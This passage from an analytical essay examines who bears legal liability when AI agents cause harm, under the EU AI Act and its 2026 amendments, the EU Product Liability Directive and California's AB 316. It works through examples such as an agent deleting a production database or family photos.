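The EU AI Act doesn't define "agent". According to the European Commission's *How are AI agents addressed within the AI Act?*, the Act's definitions of AI systems and general-purpose models are enough to cover agents, though the Commission calls its thinking on agents "only preliminary".

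Nannini and colleagues explain that when a company builds an agent on another company's model, the Act treats the model and the agent as separate. The model's provider, the agent's provider and the organisation that deploys the agent each have their own duties. The Act has no separate category for harness builders. Whoever offers the finished system is normally its provider, so Anthropic would be the provider of both Claude and Claude Code.

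The Act's strictest rules apply to high-risk systems, and whether a system counts as high-risk depends mainly on what people use it for. In Nannini and colleagues' mapping, an agent that ranks job applicants is high-risk, but a coding agent that can change live systems usually isn't, even if it can delete a company's database. Other EU laws may still apply to the software the coding agent produces.

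The EU AI Act requires providers of high-risk systems to manage risks, build in logging and human oversight, and protect the systems against attack. Article 26 requires deployers to follow the provider's instructions, assign competent people to oversee the system, monitor it and keep its logs. Nannini and colleagues infer from the Act's cybersecurity requirement that providers will have to limit an agent's privileges outside the model, though the European standards that should settle the details were unfinished when they wrote. They also conclude that a high-risk agent can't currently meet the Act's requirements if nobody can trace how its behaviour drifts.

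The European Union amended its AI Act in July 2026, postponing the rules for high-risk systems. Most systems on the market before the new dates come under these rules only if their design later changes significantly. The amendments also add duties to share information. Someone who turns an existing system into a high-risk one becomes its provider, and the original provider must tell them about known limitations and failure modes and give them access for testing. The original provider can avoid these duties by clearly stating that nobody may turn its system into a high-risk one.

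Companies that supply models, tools or other components for a high-risk system must also agree in writing what information and technical access they will provide. Free and open-source tools are exempt, but general-purpose models are not. Suppliers that break these rules can be fined. Providers of high-risk systems can therefore use the law to obtain miss rates and test results from their suppliers, though the amendments don't mention either by name.

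The EU's AI Office enforces the AI Act for systems whose provider also made the underlying model, and national authorities enforce it for most others, according to the European Commission's *Commission starts enforcing AI Act rules and new transparency requirements*. Claude Code would fall under the AI Office, and an online shop's assistant built on Claude would fall under a national authority.

The European Union's new Product Liability Directive, *Directive (EU) 2024/2853* (2024), concerns compensation for harm and counts software as a product. Claimants have to prove that the product was defective and caused the damage, but they don't have to prove negligence. If technical complexity makes the proof excessively difficult, a court must presume the defect or the causal link, as long as the claimant shows that it is likely. The manufacturer can then try to rebut the presumption.

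Under its provisions, a manufacturer's liability doesn't shrink because a third party also contributed to the damage, so a company whose defective agent obeyed an injected instruction can't reduce what it owes by blaming the attacker. It also can't exclude its liability to the injured person by contract. A court may reduce the compensation if the injured person was also at fault, and manufacturers will probably argue that users who approved the harmful command were at fault.

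It is less clear when a missed action counts as a defect. The test is whether the product provides the safety that people are entitled to expect, taking into account its presentation and instructions. A warning that a classifier doesn't guarantee safety would therefore help its maker somewhat. But if a product's purpose is to prevent damage, failing to do so counts against it, and this could apply to a guardrail that a company sells separately. Courts will have to decide whether a guardrail with an 11% miss rate is defective each time it misses an action, or only if it misses more often than its maker led people to expect.

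The directive covers injury to people, damage to their property and the destruction of their data. It excludes property that someone uses only for work and data used for professional purposes. If an agent deleted someone's family photos, that person could claim, but a company in PocketOS's position couldn't claim for its production database. It would have to rely on its contracts and on other national law.

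California took a narrower step with *Assembly Bill No. 316* (AB 316), which the governor approved on 13 October 2025. The bill added *Civil Code section 1714.46*, which bars a defendant who developed, modified or used AI from arguing that the AI caused the harm autonomously.

The section rules out one excuse, but the injured party still has to establish that the defendant is liable. The law firm Baker Botts describes accountability as shifting to whoever built, modified or deployed the system, which is true only in this limited sense. Defendants can still dispute causation, argue that the harm was unforeseeable, and present evidence that someone else was at fault. A user could argue that the harness ignored a deny rule, and the harness builder could reply that the user had left a powerful token where the agent could read it.

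### Liability and the ability to prevent harm

The party that can prevent harm most cheaply isn't always the one that has to pay for it. Railway, for example, could have made the PocketOS deletion reversible by changing its own service. But it neither developed nor used the agent, so AB 316 has little bearing on its liability, and the Product Liability Directive excludes the lost business data. Any duty to compensate PocketOS would have to come from a contract or general negligence law. Railway changed its service within days anyway, probably because customers would leave a provider that let one request destroy their data.

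Liability can also fall on a company with little control over the cause. Suppose a small firm uses a large developer's model in an app that organises family photos. The model misreads a request and the app deletes an album. Under the directive, the firm is liable for defects in the components it integrates, although it can't retrain the model. It can try to recover the compensation it pays from the developer. But the directive exempts the developer from liability if it proves that the fault lay in the design of the app, which let the model delete photos without a way to restore them.

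The firm would be unwise to rely on someone else paying for the model's mistakes. It can't change how often the model misreads a request, but it can keep deleted photos for 30 days, which would make most mistakes harmless.

Outside the high-risk category, the AI Act doesn't require a supplier to share its failure rates with the companies that build on its model, so a deploying organisation has to ask for them before it signs a contract. If the supplier won't provide them, the organisation should assume the miss rate is high and spend its money on limiting the damage each completed action can do.
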